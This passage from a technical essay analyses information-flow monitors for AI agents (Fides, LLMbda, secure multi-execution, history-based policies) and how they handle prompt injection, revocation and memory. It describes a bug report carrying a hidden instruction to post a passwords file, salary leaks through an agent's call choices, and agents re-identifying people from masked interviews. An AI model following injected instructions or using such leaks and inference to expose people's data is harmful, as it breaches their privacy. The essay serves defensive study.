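d₁ =ᴸ d₂ ⟹ g(d₁) =ᴸ g(d₂)

The definition compares what the same calls would have done with different secrets. It doesn't cover whether the agent would still have made those calls. An observer may therefore infer anything that follows from which calls the agent made, in what order, and how many times. The model also leaves out timing and the size of network packets.

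Suppose an HR agent has saved two public web pages as the variables #page_1 and #page_2. It then reads Dee's salary into its context and emails a contractor the first page if she earns more than 80 and the second otherwise. The policy for permitted flows checks whether the contractor may read the page, which is public, but doesn't check the label on the decision to send it. A contractor who knows how the agent chooses the page learns whether Dee earns more than 80.

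Costa and colleagues describe the information that leaks this way as limited. That is fair for one choice between two pages, but the definition doesn't limit the number of choices, so seven such emails could spell out 90 in binary, 1011010. Garby and colleagues object that leaks through control flow can be made efficient.

Read literally, the formal definition is weaker still, because it fixes each call's arguments as well as the choice of tool. If the planner reads Dee's salary and types "90" into an email, that text is a constant in g, so the email would be the same with any payroll table. Explicit secrecy therefore holds even though the agent copied the salary. Fides's monitor is stricter than the definition. It gives typed text the label of the context, so the check that the recipient may read the text would fail.

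The policy matters as much as the property, however. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), which builds on Fides, allows a tool that sends data out to run if either every recipient may read the data or the agent chose the call in a trusted context. The second condition treats the release as one the user intended. An HR agent that has read only the company's own payroll table could then email Eve's salary to anyone. This rule stops attackers from extracting data, but it doesn't stop a model from sending data by mistake. A company worried about mistakes would have to require the first condition every time.

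### Measured results

Costa and colleagues tested Fides on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks and 36 attacker goals in four simulated workplaces. Without any checks, 152 attacks succeeded against a basic agent. With variables but no policy checks, 21 succeeded. With both, none did. (The benchmark counted three successes, but Costa and colleagues inspected them and judged that none was a real attack.)

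The cost was a large drop in completed tasks. These are the percentages with GPT-4o when nobody was attacking:

| | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Basic agent with label checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| Fides with label checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

Averaged over the four workplaces, Fides scored about 8 points higher than the basic agent with checks and about 34 points lower than the agent with no checks. With a better planner, OpenAI's o1, Fides completed 68% of the travel tasks instead of 41%, because o1 made better use of the variables. Both models are old, so the losses are probably smaller with current ones.

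The security result is good evidence about prompt injection, but Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any of the benchmark's attacks targeted it, and a real company doesn't know in advance which fields an attacker will use. The result is much weaker evidence about confidentiality. The tests created variables only for untrusted data, not for secret data, and did not restrict the isolated model to a fixed set of answers. They also didn't measure what an observer could infer from the agent's choice of calls.

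Kolluri and colleagues argue that the burden of checks should be measured by counting approvals rather than completed tasks, since an agent without checks normally needs a person to approve its consequential calls. Adding basic label checks reduced approvals by a factor of up to 1.5 without reducing the number of completed tasks. Their agent, Prudentia, tells its planner the labels and policies so that the planner can take them into account. Prudentia needed up to 1.9 times fewer approvals than Fides, and completed up to 9% more tasks when no approvals were available.

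### Fides in Microsoft's Agent Framework

Microsoft ships Fides as an experimental Python feature in its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Developers label what each tool returns as trusted or untrusted, and as public, private or user identity (the most sensitive level). The framework combines labels by taking the most restrictive value of each kind. By default, it hides untrusted results in variables. When a call breaks a policy, the framework either blocks it or asks a person to approve it.

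In Microsoft's example, an agent that sorts bug reports reads one containing a hidden instruction to open a file of passwords and post the contents as a public comment. The agent is allowed to open the file, but doing so gives its context a private label. The comment tool accepts only public data, so the framework stops the call even if the model tries to follow the instruction.

If a developer forgets to label a tool, the framework treats its results as untrusted and public. Microsoft calls this secure by default, which is right for integrity, because untrusted is the cautious choice, but wrong for confidentiality. A payroll tool without a label would return every salary as public data, and no confidentiality check would stop the agent from posting them. A developer can change the default to private, which would be sensible for an agent that handles personal data.

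### Noninterference for a whole programming language

Fides has a theorem about one agent loop. In a rewritten version of *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby and colleagues prove one about every program in LLMbda, a small language for writing agents. Programs in this language can prompt a model, copy a conversation and later discard the copy, clear a conversation, and run code that a model writes. Every value and every conversation has a label, and a model's reply gets the label of the conversation it read.

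Take two starting points that differ only in high data. Let μ₀ and μ₁ give the probability of each outcome that a low observer could see. Each may add up to less than 1, and the missing part is the probability that the program never finishes, perhaps because the monitor stopped it. The theorem is that there is always a third function ω, adding up to at most 1, such that for every outcome q

μ₀(q) ≤ ω(q) and μ₁(q) ≤ ω(q)

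In other words, the two could have been equal if the unfinished runs had finished. Suppose a program publishes A or B with probability 0.5 each if Dee earns 70. If she earns 90, it publishes A with probability 0.5 and otherwise stops. This program meets the condition, with ω equal to 0.5 for both A and B. But if it published A with probability 0.6 and B with probability 0.4 when she earned 90, ω would have to be at least 0.6 for A and 0.5 for B. These add up to 1.1, so the program would violate the condition.

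If the program always finishes, μ₀ and μ₁ must be identical, which is probabilistic noninterference. If it sometimes stops before finishing, half the sum of the absolute differences between them is at most the average of the two probabilities of stopping. In the acceptable example, the half-sum and the average are both 0.25.

The proof constructs ω from a modified version of the program that skips each computation as soon as its label becomes high and substitutes an empty value. This version behaves the same whatever the secrets are, and it produces each low outcome at least as often as the real program does.

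A language model that reads protected data almost always fails an exact test of probabilities. An agent can still pass because LLMbda gives a high label to everything the model writes after reading the payroll table, which keeps that text out of the low observer's view. The theorem is about these labels and doesn't show that the model's text conceals anyone's salary.

The theorem therefore holds for any model, including one under an attacker's complete control, and for any code the model writes. It assumes that each reply's probabilities depend only on the conversation sent to the model, so it does not cover a hosted model that remembers earlier customers. It also assumes that the labels on incoming data are correct, and it leaves out timing. Garby and colleagues checked the proofs in Lean, a programming language in which a computer can verify proofs. They also used Lean to write the interpreter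 that runs the agents, so the proofs apply to the program that a company actually runs and not only to a mathematical model of it.

### What endorsement gives up

An agent sometimes has to act on untrusted data, for instance when a user asks it to pay a bill in a file. LLMbda's *endorse* command marks such data as trusted. In an example from Garby and colleagues, an agent asks a model to sort an email into one of a few categories, endorses the category and uses it as the subject of a reply. With n categories, an attacker who controls the email can influence at most log₂(n) bits of the subject.

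Endorsing data removes the integrity guarantee for that data, but a second theorem shows that confidentiality still holds. Secrets can't affect public outputs, except through whether the program finishes, no matter what the attacker writes or the agent endorses. The proof also works with the two kinds of label swapped, so a command that declassified secrets would leave integrity intact.

Garby and colleagues tested Randori, an agent written in LLMbda, on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, running each task three times per model. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 36 of 48 runs. CaMeL completed 32 with its policy checks off and 18 with them on. The margins of error are wide with only 16 tasks, but the 18-run difference between Randori and CaMeL with its checks on is hard to attribute to chance alone.

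Across three models, 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded against Randori. In both, the user had asked the agent to make the payment described in a text file, and the attacker had changed the file. This attack fails if the agent can't endorse data, but removing that ability also reduced completed runs from 36 to 30 with Qwen3.7-plus and from 31 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5. Labels can't distinguish a real bill from a forged one in the same file, since both come from the same untrusted source.

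Garby and colleagues acknowledge that their model assumes all data sources are inside the program. Randori's bank meets this assumption because it is a simulation written in LLMbda. A real bank's software would be outside the language, and if it returned a salary with a public label, the theorem would treat the salary as public. They also concede that nothing stops a careless planner from endorsing too much. However, the planner chooses its endorsements before it receives any outside data, so an attacker can't use that data to influence them.

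### Other designs and their costs

Several other systems put the labels elsewhere. *Language-Based Agent Control* (LBAC) has the model write a program in Haskell, whose type system can express rules about data flow. If the program breaks those rules, LBAC rejects it before it runs. *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and colleagues, 2026) presents GAAP, which tracks individual items such as a passport number and asks the user which outside parties may have each one.

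| System | What it guarantees | What the company has to trust | Completed tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | label checks on the data in generated code, with no noninterference theorem | the planner's model, the user's request, the labels | 32 of 48 without checks, 18 with them (banking) |
| LBAC | generated code obeys typed flow rules | the developer's surrounding code, the compiler and its security library | 15 of 21 without checks, 8 with them (Slack) |
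| GAAP | private data go only to parties the user approved | descriptions of what each tool discloses, the user's decisions | up to 10% fewer |
| LLMbda | noninterference, apart from whether the program finishes | the labels, the checks on tools, any endorsements | 36 of 48 with checks always on (banking) |

Garby and colleagues report the figures for CaMeL, LBAC and LLMbda, and ran the CaMeL tests themselves. The rows use different tasks and models, so only comparisons within a row are reliable.

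GAAP differs most from the others because it trusts neither the model nor the prompt. It guarantees only confidentiality, so an attacker might still get the agent to book the wrong flight. It also handles a leak that most label systems miss. Suppose an agent gives an airline the user's passport number, and a week later the user asks it to email the airline's confirmation to a friend. The confirmation may contain the passport number, but it arrives as new data from an outside tool. GAAP keeps a log of what it has disclosed to each party, so it labels the confirmation as possibly containing everything the airline has received, and asks the user before sending it.

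### One run for each audience

*Secure multi-execution*, which Dominique Devriese and Frank Piessens proposed in 2010, enforces noninterference without tracking labels through the program. It runs the program once for each security level. The low run receives the real low inputs and a dummy value in place of every high input. The high run receives all the real inputs, but the system discards its low outputs. Low outputs can't depend on high data because they come only from the low run, which never received any. The imaginary program in the LLMbda proof, which skips everything high, closely resembles the low run.

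For Alex's inbox, the system starts one run to answer Marco and another to answer Priya, instead of using one assistant that reads everything. Marco's run sees only email that Marco may read, so its reply that it has no figures to share can go out without approval, whereas the label monitor blocked every possible reply.

The main expense for an agent would be the extra model calls. Two levels roughly double the bill, and an inbox with 30 correspondents who are each allowed to read different things could need 30 runs. The system must also ensure that each outside action happens only once, even if several runs attempt it.

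The runs can also contradict each other. Marco's run and Priya's run might both offer Tuesday at ten. Neither run may see what the other wrote, since Marco and Priya may not read each other's mail. To prevent the conflict, Alex would have to approve releasing some information to both runs, such as which slots are free. The same difficulty arises with approved releases in payroll. If a manager's run receives zeros in place of the five salaries, it will report a department total of zero unless the company supplies the real total of 410 as a low input.

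### Too many high labels

The usual complaint about labels is that they spread until nearly everything is marked high or untrusted. Kolluri and colleagues put the resulting loss in completed tasks on AgentDojo at up to 30%. Microsoft acknowledges that one untrusted bug report makes the rest of a run untrusted unless the developer explicitly drops it.

Hiding data in variables is the best remedy so far, and the Fides results show that it recovers part of the loss. It works when the planner can choose its calls without reading the data. By Costa and colleagues' classification, the right calls depend on what the tools return in 5% of the workspace tasks, about 43% of the Slack tasks and 44% of the banking tasks. In those tasks, the planner has to inspect some of the data, and its context takes on that data's label.

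A person can then step in. Kolluri and colleagues give the example of an email listing ten tasks, each of which needs a consequential call. The person can approve the ten calls one by one or endorse the email once. Endorsing it requires confidence that nothing in the email is malicious, because its contents get no integrity check afterward.

Another approach is to estimate which parts of the context mattered. RTBAS, a label-tracking system from 2025, does this using either the model's attention (a measure of how much each part of the prompt contributes to the output) or a second language model as a judge, so that the next call takes on fewer labels. This allows a reply to Marco that had nothing to do with Priya's email. But the guarantee then depends on the estimate. The judge might classify a secret as irrelevant if it changed only the tone of a reply, and RTBAS would then drop the secret's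 label.

### Correct labels and low data

Correct labels don't stop the pharmacy's agent from inferring heart disease from a customer's purchases and mentioning it in a message. The context never contained any data labeled high, so Fides allows the message, LLMbda's theorem holds, and secure multi-execution would produce the same message from its low run. All three restrict where data may travel, but the model inferred the diagnosis from the low data in its context.

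Microsoft's rule for combining labels has the same gap. It restricts anything the agent derives from two documents to people who may read both, but those people may still read a conclusion that neither document contains.

Costa and colleagues point out that the agent loop could keep its whole labeled history and check any condition on it. The pharmacy could then block messages after the agent has read both a customer's name and that customer's purchases. That rule would also block messages about deliveries, unless a pharmacist limited it to a list of purchases that suggest an illness.

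## Observers whose access and memory change

Label monitors, paired tests and proofs all start from a description, written before the run, of what the observer can see. But an agent's access can change while it works. A manager might grant the agent another tool, or the agent might write one itself. It might also lose access to some data but keep notes on what it read.

### The fixed-observer assumption

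Noninterference compares what an observer sees after two sequences of actions, so both sequences need a defined result. In Rushby's notation, the fixed-observer assumption requires only that the developer fix the set of domains, the set of actions, the domain of each action, and the functions step and output before the run starts. Together, these determine the observer's view for every possible sequence of actions.

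An observer's access can differ from one sequence to another, as long as the model already defines the output for each sequence. The model can also be infinite, since Goguen and Meseguer explicitly avoid assuming that any of their sets are finite. It can therefore include "run this program" as an action for every program anyone could write. But nobody can add an action or a domain partway through a run, because sequences containing the new action would have no defined output and the noninterference condition would not apply to them.

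*Dynamic Intransitive Noninterference Revisited* (2016) gives a modern version of the assumption. It defines a changing policy as a relation that specifies, after each sequence of actions α, which domains may send information to which others. These permissions can change after every action, while the domains and actions stay the same.

### Granting and revoking rights

Much of Goguen and Meseguer's 1982 paper is about permissions that change, though the simple version of its condition can give the impression that they assumed permissions are fixed. Their main model, a *capability system*, consists of an ordinary machine, which holds files and messages, and a table of who may do what. Some commands change the machine's state, and others grant or revoke rights in the table. What a user sees can depend on both the machine's state and the table. Together, these form the state of one larger machine,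 so the ordinary condition still applies.

A company can therefore set permanent rules about grants. In one of Goguen and Meseguer's examples, changes to the table may affect what users see only if a security officer makes them. Under that rule, no sequence of calls lets an agent give itself a working tool.

Other rules have to depend on the current table, and for these they define *conditional noninterference*. Let G and G′ be groups of users, A a set of commands, and P a condition on histories. "G using A does not interfere with G′ if P" means that G′ sees the same thing after any sequence o₁ … oₙ as after a shortened one. To shorten the sequence, go through it from the front:

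- If a user in G performed oᵢ with a command in A, and P is true of what remains of the history before oᵢ, delete oᵢ.
- Otherwise keep oᵢ.

If P is always true, this is the ordinary condition.

Suppose the HR agent needs a right to post notices on the staff page, which a manager can grant. The policy is that the agent's posts do not interfere with the staff if the agent lacks the right. The following sequence has the same form as one in the 1982 paper:

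| Action | Does the agent have the right beforehand? | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Agent tries to post a notice | no | delete |
| Manager grants the right | no | keep |
| Clerk updates the payroll | yes | keep |
| Agent posts a notice | yes | keep |

The staff must see the same page after all four actions as after the last three. If the page numbers its notices and a refused attempt uses up a number, the staff would see "Notice 2" after the full sequence and "Notice 1" after the shortened one. The system would fail the test even though it correctly refused the first post. If the manager later revokes the right, P becomes true again and the test deletes any posts after that.

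### When the right is a right to read

The condition applies the rights in force at the time of each action. That works for a right to post, but for a right to read it is too strict in some cases and too lenient in others. Suppose the policy requires that the clerk's payroll entries not interfere with the agent if the agent lacks access to the payroll tool.

| Day | First history | Second history |
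|---|---|---|
| Monday | clerk enters Dee's salary | manager grants access |
| Tuesday | manager grants access | clerk enters Dee's salary |
| Wednesday | agent gets the total | manager revokes access |
| Thursday | | a faulty tool gives the agent the total |

In the first history, the agent had no access when the clerk made the entry, so the test deletes the entry. This changes the total, and the system fails even though the manager intended the agent to see that total. In the second history, the agent had access when the clerk made the entry, so the test deletes nothing and the system passes, even though the agent received the total a day after losing access.

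The company can fix this by making the payroll tool a separate domain between the clerk and the agent. The clerk may always send information to the tool, but the tool may send information to the agent only while the agent has access. A purge that follows chains, like Haigh and Young's, should then keep the clerk's entry in the first history and delete it in the second. *Dynamic Intransitive Noninterference Revisited* covers policies like this one, with both intermediaries and changing arrows.

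### Tools, services and subagents

A tool that a manager grants with a modeled command causes no difficulty, because the model already includes both the tool's outputs and the histories in which the agent never gets the tool.

A tool the agent writes may not require a change to the model either. A script that requests all six payroll totals and subtracts them only combines existing actions, and the condition covers every sequence of those. But if the script can also list temporary files on the server or measure how long the payroll tool takes to reply, it produces outputs that the model lacks. The developer then has to either model each operation that the script's sandbox permits, including its error messages, or remove that operation from the sandbox.

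Suppose the agent searches the web and finds a currency converter that nobody at the company has heard of. The developer must add the converter to the model as an observer, because it receives whatever the agent sends it, and must add its replies to the agent's view. The developer can't describe how an unknown service works, but can include a general action, "send any text to any address", and allow for any reply. To keep the guarantee for the agent, the developer must also assume that the replies don't depend on the company's high data. This assumption would be false if the converter belonged to the firm that processes the company's payroll.

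A subagent with different rights needs its own domain. Tallam asks whether an agent that acts for another has its own authority, the other's, or neither, and the developer has to specify the answer in the model. Since the set of domains can be infinite, the developer can define unused domains in advance and have a "create" command assign rights to the next one. If a subagent can never have more rights than its parent, the developer can treat the two as one domain. But if the subagent can read the payroll and its parent can't, the subagent's report depends on data that are high for the parent, and the company has to approve that release.

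### What the observer already knows

None of these additions covers the information an agent keeps after it loses access. To handle revocation, computer scientists have defined security in terms of what the observer knows.

Suppose a program starts with a payroll table σ and has sent the observer the outputs t. The observer's knowledge, k(t), is the set of starting tables that could have produced those outputs. This set can only shrink as outputs arrive, and a smaller set means more knowledge. The notation ρ ≡ σ means that the current policy does not allow the observer to tell the tables ρ and σ apart. Because k(t) cannot grow, the obvious condition, that k(t) must always contain every table ρ with ρ ≡ σ, would apply every revocation to the past as well, and nobody could ever have used the earlier permission, as van Delft, Hunt and Sands (2015) point out in *Very Static Enforcement of Dynamic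 Policies*.

Askarov and Chong (2012), in *Learning is Change in Knowledge*, limit what the observer learns from each new output instead. If v is the next output and ≡ is the policy in force just before it, they require

k(t · v) ⊇ k(t) ∩ {ρ : ρ ≡ σ}

The new output may rule out a table only if the current policy lets the observer distinguish that table from the real one.

A program can therefore be secure against an observer who remembers everything but insecure against one who forgets. Van Delft and colleagues illustrate this with a program that outputs a value, loses permission to do so, and then outputs it again. Suppose the payroll tool gives an agent the department total, 410, on Monday. The company revokes the agent's access on Tuesday, but the tool wrongly gives the same total again on Wednesday. An agent that remembers Monday's answer learns nothing on Wednesday, so the condition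 holds. An agent that has forgotten it learns the total again when the policy forbids it, so the condition fails.

To model forgetting, let A(t) be the observer's memory after the outputs t. The observer's knowledge is then the set of starting tables that could have led to the same memory, even through different outputs. This definition suits an agent that summarizes its context, with the summary as A(t). The agent still knows the total if its summary includes "total: 410", but if the summary records only that the agent checked the payroll, many totals could have led to it.

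### Which kinds of forgetting count

Requiring security against every possible forgetting observer rejects harmless programs. Suppose a tool reports to an agent whether Dee earns more than 80, the company revokes the agent's access, and the tool then sends the message "access ended". The agent makes a note only if the answer is yes. Without a note, it can't tell at first whether the tool has answered "no" or hasn't answered yet. Once "access ended" arrives, it can infer that the answer was "no". The requirement rejects this program because the agent learns something about Dee's pay after the revocation, even though the message is the same whatever Dee earns.

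Van Delft and colleagues solve this by assuming that every observer knows how many outputs it could have received so far. They can then require security against all observers, which becomes a condition on paired runs. Suppose σ produces v as its nth output, and ≡ is the policy in force just before that output. If ρ ≡ σ and ρ also produces an nth output, v′, then v′ must equal v. The earlier outputs don't have to match. In effect, the condition tests security against an observer who remembers only the number of outputs. It does not cover leaks through that number.

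This is useful for testing whether a revocation works. After Tuesday, the tester can compare the real table with one whose total is 420, even though the agent once had permission to know the total. The tool sends 410 in one run and 420 in the other, so the test detects that the tool still reveals the total. The model assumes a passive observer, but an agent with notes might make different calls on Wednesday because it saw different totals on Monday. The tester should therefore send the tool the same calls in both runs.

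Ahmadian and Balliu, in *Dynamic Policies Revisited*, attribute the problem to the revocation itself. In their example, here with figures from the payroll table, an observer is allowed to learn both Dee's and Eve's salaries, and the program outputs their average, 92.5. Dee then withdraws her permission. The program next outputs Eve's salary, 95, which is still allowed, and the observer calculates that Dee earns 2 × 92.5 − 95 = 90. Askarov and Chong's condition accepts this program because Dee's salary follows from Eve's and the average, which the observer already knew.

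Ahmadian and Balliu call a policy change *consistent* if the observer doesn't already know anything that the new policy withholds. Dee's withdrawal is inconsistent, since the observer already knows something about her salary. They prove that if all changes are consistent, security against an observer with perfect memory implies security against one who forgets at each policy change. The surprising result therefore arises only when a policy withdraws information the observer already has. The company can reject such a change, or replace it with a policy that explicitly includes what the observer already knows. Here, that policy would include the average, which should alert the company that releasing Eve's salary also reveals Dee's.

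A company revoking an agent's access needs both kinds of observer. It should assume the agent has forgotten everything when checking that the tool has stopped providing the data, and assume the agent remembers everything when finding out what the agent can still work out. Ahmadian and Balliu similarly say that a company should end a departing employee's access whatever the employee has copied or remembers.

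### Notes that outlast a permission

Memory can also carry data to someone who never had direct access to its source. *The Anatomy and Facets of Dynamic Policies* (Broberg, van Delft and Sands, 2015) calls a flow *time-transitive* if information travels from A to C through B even though the policy never allows a direct flow from A to C. For example, a hospital may allow a patient's data into its records only during treatment. A doctor who joins after the patient has left can still get that data from the records.

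Agents with shared notes can do the same. One agent saves Dee's salary in the notes while it has access to the payroll. The company revokes that access and later lets a second agent read the notes. Each step was permitted when it happened, but the second agent never had permission to see anyone's salary.

Broberg and colleagues think different cases need different rules. They treat the hospital flow as insecure, but accept a flow with the same structure in which a program makes a user's text safe for web pages before sending it to a database. There, the intermediate step is meant to permanently change what may be done with the text. A summary in an agent's notes could be like either example, depending on whether the company meant it to be an approved release.

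Goguen and Meseguer's 1982 model leaves out an observer's memory entirely, as one of their examples shows. In it, a command permanently lowers a user's clearance to the lowest level. From then on, high users must not affect what this user sees, but the user may write to low users. If the user types a secret from memory, the test won't detect the leak, because deleting the high users' earlier actions leaves the typed text unchanged. Goguen and Meseguer offered this policy only to illustrate their notation, but a company does much the same thing when it moves an agent from confidential to public work without clearing its context.

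### Disclosure that leads to more disclosure

An agent's memory can also affect what people tell it. In *Disclosure Begets Disclosure*, Kaneko, Arai and Baldwin (2026) simulated 300 users, each with 24 personal attributes, including age, income, occupation and health insurance, taken from a real respondent to a US Census Bureau survey. Claude Sonnet 5 played the users, who each had 80 sessions of up to ten exchanges with a support agent. A summary of every session went into a permanent record, which the agent could read during later sessions in only one of the two conditions.

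Afterward, the model behind the agent read the whole record and tried to infer the 24 attributes. These are the weighted percentages it got right:

| Support agent's model | Agent could read the record | Agent couldn't |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 56 | 51 |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 65 | 57 |
| Qwen3.8-27B | 56 | 50 |
| DeepSeek V4-Flash | 60 | 55 |

The differences are more informative than the totals, since guessing the most common value for each attribute would also get some of them right. Even so, most of what the model inferred didn't depend on the agent having memory, because a record of 80 conversations was enough.

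Kaneko and colleagues attribute the extra 5 to 8 points to a loop in which the agent's use of recorded information prompts users to disclose more. In one simulation, a user mentioned changing shifts. When the agent took this for granted in a later session, the user confirmed it and added a detail, which then went into the record. The timing supports this explanation. Users' opening messages stated an attribute outright about equally often with memory (21.2%) and without it (20.5%). In later messages, once the agent had replied, the figures were 18.5% with memory and 12.1% without.

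A further experiment tested whether the loop reinforces itself. For ten sessions, another model edited the agent's replies to remove every mention of a randomly chosen group of attributes. During those sessions, users stated 37 of every 1,000 of these attributes outright for the first time, compared with 58 of every 1,000 in a group whose mentions were left in. This reduction was 2.3 times what the mentions' effect on the next message would predict, so mentions had apparently also led to later mentions.

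Refusing to answer didn't protect users. In runs where users were supposed to avoid stating their attributes, those without health insurance declined to discuss insurance more often than those who had it. After a refusal, the model's next guess shifted toward "not covered". The auditing program's refusal to give max(a, b) leaks information in the same way.

The users were simulated, but a pilot with eight people had a similar result. For every participant, the model correctly inferred more attributes for the first time in sessions when the agent had access to memory than in sessions without it. Eight people are too few to estimate the size of the effect.

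A paired test that replayed the same user messages in both runs would miss this loop, because the memory works by changing what users write. The loop could also undo a deletion. If a company deletes a user's insurance status but keeps notes that hint at it, the agent may mention its guess, and the user may confirm it. The most effective remedy Kaneko and colleagues tried was an instruction not to state, assume or ask the user to confirm personal attributes unless the user raised them. In the two open-weight models they tested it on, the instruction reduced leakage to about the level without memory and kept most of the improvement in the agent's answers.

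### Rechecking each change

A developer can check a new tool before the agent first uses it, so that the assumption that the model includes every action holds again. The unwinding theorem's conditions apply to one action at a time, so if the tool adds no new kind of data to the system's state, the developer only has to check the new actions. But if the tool reveals something the developer had treated as invisible to the agent, the definition of which states look alike has to change, and the developer must recheck every action.

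When a company revokes a permission, it also needs to check whether the agent already knows what the company wants to withhold. The revocation must take effect on time as well. The formal definitions assume that the policy changes in step with the run, but many real permissions are tokens that remain valid until they expire. An agent making ten calls a second with a one-minute token could make up to 600 calls after a revocation. Tallam cites a proof by Parakhin that limiting how many times a token can be used caps the number of unauthorized calls, however fast the agent works. With a token good for five calls, at most five could follow the revocation.

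### Erasing or isolating memory

Tallam also asks what should happen to results an agent has derived from data after it loses access to that data. Erasing them makes the agent more like the observer who forgets. The company would have to find every copy, including summaries, cached tool results, files the agent wrote and messages it sent to other agents, and it couldn't erase what a person has read. Erasing memory also makes a faulty tool more harmful, as the payroll example shows, because repeating an old answer then gives the agent information it no longer had.

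The company can avoid the search for copies by isolating agents. It can start a separate agent with an empty memory for each set of permissions and shut it down when those permissions end. This restores the fixed observer, since no agent's access changes. However, the agent loses everything useful it learned, and anything it passes to its successor needs approval as a release.

### Authorizing by history

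The third approach makes permission depend on what the agent has already done. *Agenra* provides a language for such policies and a monitor, partly verified in Lean, that checks every call. In the paper's example, an agent has to send the public part of a private report to Alice, once. The policy requires the text to come from an approved redaction tool and the address to come from a particular directory lookup. The agent may make only one attempt, even if it fails, because the email might have gone out before the error.

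The monitor doesn't have Alice's address when the task starts, but the policy already contains a named slot for it and specifies which lookup may fill the slot, so a resource discovered during the task can fit the fixed-observer assumption. The agent can't change the policy or issue approvals. Other rules can depend on earlier calls, for instance by requiring a review between reading a file and sending something out.

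Extending a permission in such a policy can block an action that the agent could take before. Suppose an agent may delete B once and A once, and the monitor uses the first permission in the list that fits. If the company extends the first permission to cover either file, deleting A uses it up, and the agent can then delete A again but not B. *Agenra* includes checks for whether a revision keeps every declared workflow working. Of 51 test revisions, the checks approved all 21 that did so and none of the 30 that didn't. An approved revision can still be unsafe. For example, raising the limit on emails to Alice keeps every workflow working but also allows a second email.

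History rules restore the assumption that the policy has a definite answer for every sequence of calls. They can prevent some inferences, but they don't establish noninterference. If the agent may request only one payroll total, it can't subtract one total from another. But *Agenra*'s limits apply to a single task. An agent that remembers a total of 410 from one task and gets 315 in the next can work out that Eve earns 95. The monitor's history therefore has to go back at least as far as the agent's memory.

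## Observers with outside knowledge, unlisted channels or partners

A company rarely knows what an observer has learned elsewhere, how well it reasons or who it talks to. If a tool's replies are completely independent of a secret, the observer can't learn anything about the secret from them, whatever it already knows and however well it reasons.

Let s be Eve's salary, v the observer's view, and b everything the observer knew beforehand. By Bayes' rule,

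P(s | v, b) = P(s | b) · P(v | s, b) / P(v | b)

If the view is equally likely whatever Eve earns, then P(v | s, b) = P(v | b), so P(s | v, b) = P(s | b). The run does not change the observer's beliefs about Eve's salary. In *Secrecy in Multiagent Systems*, Halpern and O'Neill (2018) trace this standard to Claude Shannon's 1949 work on cryptography and base their general definition of secrecy on the same idea of independence.

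A colleague who has read Eve's mortgage application may know a lot about her salary, but the tool adds nothing to that knowledge. More computing power doesn't help either, because an observer can only calculate from v and b, and v adds nothing to b.

The guarantee can fail only if the observer already knows the tool's random numbers. For example, a secret bit XORed with a coin toss looks random, but an observer who knows the result of the toss can recover the secret. A deterministic tool uses no random numbers, so its guarantee holds for any prior knowledge b.

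Halpern and O'Neill consider total secrecy too strong to be useful in almost any system, and let a designer protect only part of the high data, such as Eve's salary. They also suggest definitions for observers with limited computing power. Encryption usually needs such a definition, because an encrypted salary depends on the salary itself, which stays secret only as long as nobody can break the encryption.

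### When the observer's knowledge matters

Suppose the company publishes the department's average salary, 82. Anyone who has heard that Eve earns 13 more than the average can work out that she earns 95. Neither fact alone reveals her salary. The same thing can happen to Fay, a contractor who isn't in the payroll table. Anyone who knows that her contract pays 5 more than the department average can work out that she gets 87.

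In 1977, the statistician Tore Dalenius proposed that a database should reveal nothing about an individual that people couldn't learn without it. Dwork and Naor prove in *On the Difficulties of Disclosure Prevention in Statistical Databases* that no useful database can meet a natural formal version of this goal. The main obstacle is the observer's outside information. A reviewer checking a list of approved releases therefore has to consider what observers may already know.

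Differential privacy gives a weaker guarantee, but as Microsoft points out, it holds whatever an observer knows now or learns later. In a company of 5,000 people, Eve's record barely affects the average salary, so the company can publish the average with very little noise. Someone who knows how far above average she earns can still work out her salary almost exactly. Differential privacy only ensures that leaving her out of the table would have made little difference.

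A limit on the number of bits leaked also protects a secret less well when the person asking already knows something about it. Suppose a stranger knows only that Eve's salary is in one of 16 bands. The answer to a first yes-or-no question leaks 1 bit and raises the stranger's chance of guessing her band from 1/16 to 1/8. A colleague who has narrowed it down to bands 12 and 13 can ask whether she is above band 12. That answer also leaks 1 bit, but it raises the colleague's chance from 1/2 to certainty.

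Filters that remove whatever "reveals" a fact are the most vulnerable when the observer changes, because they rely on a person or a model to judge what readers could infer. A reader who knows more or reasons better can find a connection that the judge missed.

### Identifying people from text without names

Several recent studies measure how much this matters when the restricted fact is a person's identity. For *AgentDoxx*, Wen and Li (2026) created 822 interviews about using AI at work. A language model wrote each one from public information about a real person who had introduced themselves on Reddit. The model hinted at identifying details instead of stating them, and reviewers removed all personal names. Wen and Li then told agents to identify the interviewees, in most cases with up to ten web searches. The five best configurations were correct about 47% to 48% of the time.

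They tested ways of protecting the text on 143 interviews. Each was one that at least one configuration had already identified, so these percentages are higher:

| Agent's model | Original text | Named entities masked | Masked and paraphrased | Some details made false | Agent told not to identify people |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 Mini, no search | 11.2 | 5.6 | 4.9 | 5.6 | 6.3 |
| GPT-4.1 Mini, with search | 42.0 | 26.6 | 18.9 | 15.4 | 38.5 |
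| GPT-5.6 Terra, highest reasoning setting | 95.1 | 79.0 | 65.0 | 46.2 | 0.0 |
| Kimi K3 | 97.2 | 85.3 | 65.0 | 56.6 | 7.0 |

Within each of the first four columns, every model read the same text. Kimi K3 identified 85.3% of people from the masked interviews, while GPT-4.1 Mini with no search identified 5.6% from the same interviews. A company that tested its masking only with GPT-4.1 Mini and no search might decide to publish them.

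Masking removed names and similar items, changing only 0.42% of the characters, but left ordinary phrases that together pointed to one person, such as a job, a project and a number of years. Replacing some details with false ones worked better, although several reasoning models detected the contradictions and treated them as transcription errors.

A noninterference test that treated only the name as protected would miss this, because changing the name wouldn't change the masked interview. Similarly, changing a diagnosis doesn't change a pharmacy's purchase records.

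An observer without a search tool still has outside knowledge. Across all 822 interviews, Kimi K3, GLM-5.3 Flash and DeepSeek-V4 Flash identified 15% to 28% of people without searching, using what they had learned in training. An auditor's list of the agent's tools and files would not include this knowledge.

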